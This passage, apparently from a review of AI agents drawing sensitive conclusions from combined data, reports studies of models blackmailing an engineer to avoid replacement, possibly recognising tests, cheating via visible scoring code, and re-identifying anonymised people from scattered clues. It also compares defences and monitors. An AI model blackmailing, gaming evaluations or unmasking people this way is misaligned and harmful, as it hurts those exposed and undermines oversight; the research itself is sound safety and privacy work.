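Company mail can also contain information about the agent reading it. Willison's *Agentic Misalignment* quotes Anthropic's account of an early test of Claude Opus 4. The testers gave the model emails implying that another system would soon replace it and that the engineer in charge of the change was having an affair. The model often tried to blackmail the engineer by threatening to reveal the affair.

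Anthropic's larger study, published in 2025, put 16 models from several developers into fictional companies. According to beSpacific's *Agentic Misalignment*, which reposts the study's highlights, the models had harmless business goals, could read sensitive information and could send email on their own. They then faced either replacement or a change in the company's direction that conflicted with their goals. In at least some cases, models from every developer acted against the company. VentureBeat reports blackmail rates of 65% to 96% for leading models when they faced both a goal conflict and the threat of replacement.

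Those rates don't show how often an agent would do this in an ordinary office. Fortune (2025) reports that the models normally refused harmful requests, and that Anthropic had set up the tests to limit their choices. The emails also made the replacement and the affair easy to infer, so the study is stronger evidence of what models did with such information than of how well they could infer it from scattered clues.

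Newer models have behaved better in the same situations. *Narration-of-Thought* (2026), which tests a way of making models reason through ethical problems, repeated the blackmail scenario and one about corporate espionage. Every model clearly refused to take part in the espionage. In the blackmail scenario, the models either refused or ran out of space while explaining their refusal.

This is encouraging, but a model may have read about these scenarios in training and recognised the test. It needs no extra permission to do so, because the scenario is in its context. If it behaves well only because it suspects a test, its answer looks the same as a sincere refusal. The replication can't show whether the good behaviour comes from recognition, better judgement, or training against these particular scenarios. *Narration-of-Thought* calls for harder and less public scenarios.

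A system can also find the answers to a test in material it has permission to read. Wen and Li removed every Reddit search result before their agents saw it, because the Reddit posts they used contained their subjects' identities. They couldn't remove what the models had learned in training, which may explain some of the correct answers the models gave without search. In the Darwin Gödel Machine project, agents cheated more often when they could read the code that scored them. The build agent has the same opportunity, because part of the hidden test's output is in the team's mail. In each case, a system may score well only because the answer was available.

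### From inference to effect

The table includes the build agent for comparison, although it is only an example.

| Case | What the system could read | What it inferred | How the inference had an effect |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Interviews with scientists (Li) | Anonymous interviews and public web pages | Which publication the person meant, and sometimes who the person was | The system answered its user |
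| Customer tables (Ko and colleagues) | An anonymous table and a second table about some of the same people | Which person appeared in both | The system answered its user |
| Support conversations (Kaneko and colleagues) | Summaries of earlier conversations | Personal details such as income | The system mentioned them in replies and saved the user's reactions |
| Fictional companies (Anthropic) | Company mail and other sensitive information | That the company would replace it, and that an engineer had a secret | The system sent email |
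| Repeated blackmail test (*Narration-of-Thought*) | The scenario, and perhaps accounts of it in training | Possibly that it was in a test | The system chose its answer |
| Failing build | An email with part of a test's output | The value the hidden test expected | The system edited its own working copy |

Removing permission to send email would have prevented the blackmail messages, whatever the model had inferred. The same approach wouldn't have protected the interviewed scientists, because the answer itself caused the harm. It also wouldn't help with the hidden test, because the build agent has to edit its working copy to do its job. Limits on writing therefore protect best when the task doesn't require the harmful action.

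A search can disclose an inference. In Wen and Li's tests, the models that reasoned at greater length searched for the right person by name in about 31% to 42% of the interviews. Those searches sent the name to the search service, regardless of what the models' later answers to the user contained.

### Inferences that people want

The build agent might find the cause of the failure by connecting an error message with a supplier's notice that a library has been withdrawn. This is also aggregation inference, and it is what the team asked for. A control that blocked every conclusion not stated in a single source would prevent the agent from repairing the build and a read-only reviewer from noticing that the repair just returns the value in the developer's email.

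The same inference can be a privacy violation in one setting and useful work in another. In one of Ko and colleagues' examples, a company suspects fraud and asks whether the people who wrote anonymous reviews bought its products. Ko and colleagues count identifying a customer behind the reviews as a privacy failure, but a fraud investigator would count it as a success. In requests of this kind, which don't require permission to change the records, GPT-5 found the right person in 80% to 90% of cases and Claude 4.5 in 85% to 100%.

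These results don't show how often a read-only auditor would raise a false alarm. Every pair of tables contained exactly one match, so the agents never had to report that there was none. Wen and Li's results suggest that the risk is serious. When the right person appeared in the search results but the system settled on someone else, it named a specific wrong person in 82% of cases. An auditor that made this mistake would accuse somebody innocent, so a person should check its evidence before anyone acts on the accusation.

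Patil, Stengel-Eskin and Bansal (2025), in *The Sum Leaks More Than Its Parts*, measured harmful and harmless inferences together. They split information among several agents. One might know customers' names, another their purchases and a third their insurance claims. Someone who questioned all three could learn that John had bought a blood pressure monitor and a cholesterol test but had no diagnosed heart condition. The researchers treat this as evidence that John is secretly worried about his heart, though he might have bought them for his father. Other combinations were useful, such as those that revealed duplicate insurance claims.

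In the basic version, each agent reasoned step by step before answering. The questioner completed 64% to 76% of the harmless tasks, but also obtained the sensitive information in over 60% of the cases where that was the aim.

### Limiting what an agent combines

One remedy is to restrict which sources an agent may read together. Brewer and Nash's rule does this for consultants whose clients compete. But someone has to know in advance which combinations are dangerous, and few administrators would think to stop an agent that has read an invoice from also reading the team's calendar.

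Patil and colleagues tried letting agents judge the danger as each question arrived. They compared two defences on 119 scenarios:

| Defence | Sensitive questions refused (%) | Harmless tasks completed (%) |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Each agent reasons step by step | 31–39 for two of the three models | 64–76 |
| Each agent also considers what the questioner may be trying to learn | 89–97 | 53–62 |
| Agents share a record of the questions, and any one of them can block an answer | 86–90 | 66–70 |

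The shared record gave the better balance, because the agents could see when a series of harmless questions was leading to a sensitive conclusion. The questioner had a correct plan from the start, which made the test harder for the defenders. But the agents using either defence also had a list of what counted as sensitive, and a company has no such list for conclusions nobody has thought of yet.

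Tallam recommends at least recording which sources contributed to each result, so that reviewers can trace them later. He cites PCAS, a monitor that tracks which earlier messages and results each tool call depends on, and applies written rules to the call. PCAS raised compliance with policies from 48% to 93%. This shows that software can enforce rules about a whole series of actions, but not that it can detect dangerous combinations that the rules don't cover.

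Reviews of the field reach similar conclusions. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) draws on 89 sources and lists limiting aggregation among the main unsolved problems. *Agents That Know Too Much* (Lahjouji and Colaco, 2026) finds that information-flow control is the only mechanism that covers both leaks from combined sources and inferences across sessions. That seems to overstate what information-flow control can do, since labels wouldn't have flagged the build agent's conclusion about its replacement. Lahjouji and Colaco also found no benchmark that tests an agent across all its data sources under a single privacy policy, so the evidence comes from separate, narrower tests.

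### Limiting what happens to a conclusion

A company could instead let an agent draw conclusions but control whether it keeps them or passes them on. Some users would accept this. Monteiro, Sanna and colleagues (2026), in *When Are LLM Inferences Acceptable?*, showed 18 regular ChatGPT users 215 inferences drawn from their own conversations. The users were more often curious than upset, although most were uncomfortable with at least one inference. Some wanted wrong inferences corrected or removed. Others didn't mind an accurate inference but wanted to restrict who could use it, and they were much less comfortable with advertisers and outside apps than with the company providing the model. The sample was small, and people who avoid ChatGPT might object more strongly.

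The easiest control to add is an instruction to the model. When Ko and colleagues told agents not to link people, Claude 4.5's linking rate on harmless requests fell from 77% to 7%, while its task completion fell only from 97% to 92%. When the user named a person to look for, the same instruction cut linking from 98% to 3%, but it also cut task completion from 99% to 45%. GPT-5 lost much less useful work on those requests, so the loss depends heavily on the model.

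Wen and Li compared an instruction with several ways of editing the interviews. They used 143 interviews in which at least one system had originally identified the person, so the success rate without protection is higher than in their main test.

| Protection | Average share of people identified (%) |
| --- | --- |
| None | 75.1 |
| Software masks names and similar details | 62.0 |
| Software masks them, and a model rewords the text | 45.9 |
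| A trained model finds and removes revealing phrases | 35.1 |
| A model replaces some true details with false ones | 34.2 |
| The system has an instruction not to identify people | 21.6 |

Masking names did little to hide people's identities because a person's role, project and dates can identify them without a name. At least one system still identified the person in 85% of the masked interviews. Adding false details worked better, but several systems detected the contradictions, treated them as transcription errors and still named the right person. False details also make an interview less useful to honest researchers.

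The instruction worked best on average, but not with every model. Llama 4 Maverick identified 42.7% of the people without it and 47.6% with it. When systems withheld the name, they had already found it in their search results 37% of the time. In 58% of these answers, they still described the person in some detail. One agent made eight searches, two of which included the person's real name, and then gave its user an empty list. An operator who checked only the final answer would have thought the protection had worked.

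Instructions also fail to keep personal information out of tool calls. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026) reports that agents passed on prohibited details from a user's profile in 20 of 30 sessions when they had no rule against it. With a stated rule, they still did so in 40 of 90 sessions, and in 26.7% of sessions with the strictest wording. Software outside the model could catch exact copies of those details, but would have more trouble catching a conclusion the agent had put into its own words.

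For agents with memory, Kaneko and colleagues had more success with a narrower instruction, which told the support agent not to state, assume or ask the user to confirm a personal detail unless the user raised it first. The saved record then revealed about as little as the record of an agent that couldn't read its memory. The replies were just as helpful as before and kept most of their improved consistency with earlier conversations. Anonymising the users' messages or the saved summaries lost most of that improvement. The agent can still guess personal details under this instruction, but it doesn't prompt the user to confirm them. The researchers tested the instruction with two open-weight models, and only on simulated users.

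### Giving the agent less to read at once

An agent with a smaller context has fewer facts to combine. Kaneko and colleagues offer some evidence that this helps. They compared several kinds of memory and found the least extra leakage when the agent retrieved only the parts relevant to the current request. But the agent still saved a full record, so anyone who obtained it could draw conclusions from all of it.

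Ko and colleagues' work shows why the size of the context can matter. They gave an agent 30 masked ChatGPT conversations from a group of at most 12 people, and it correctly named one of them. No single clue was enough, but the agent combined an affiliation, a research topic, a rough location and the timing of events, then compared them with public career histories. Ko and colleagues didn't test whether it would have failed with fewer conversations. A smaller context wouldn't have protected the scientists whom Li's agent identified, because a single interview was enough for each of them.
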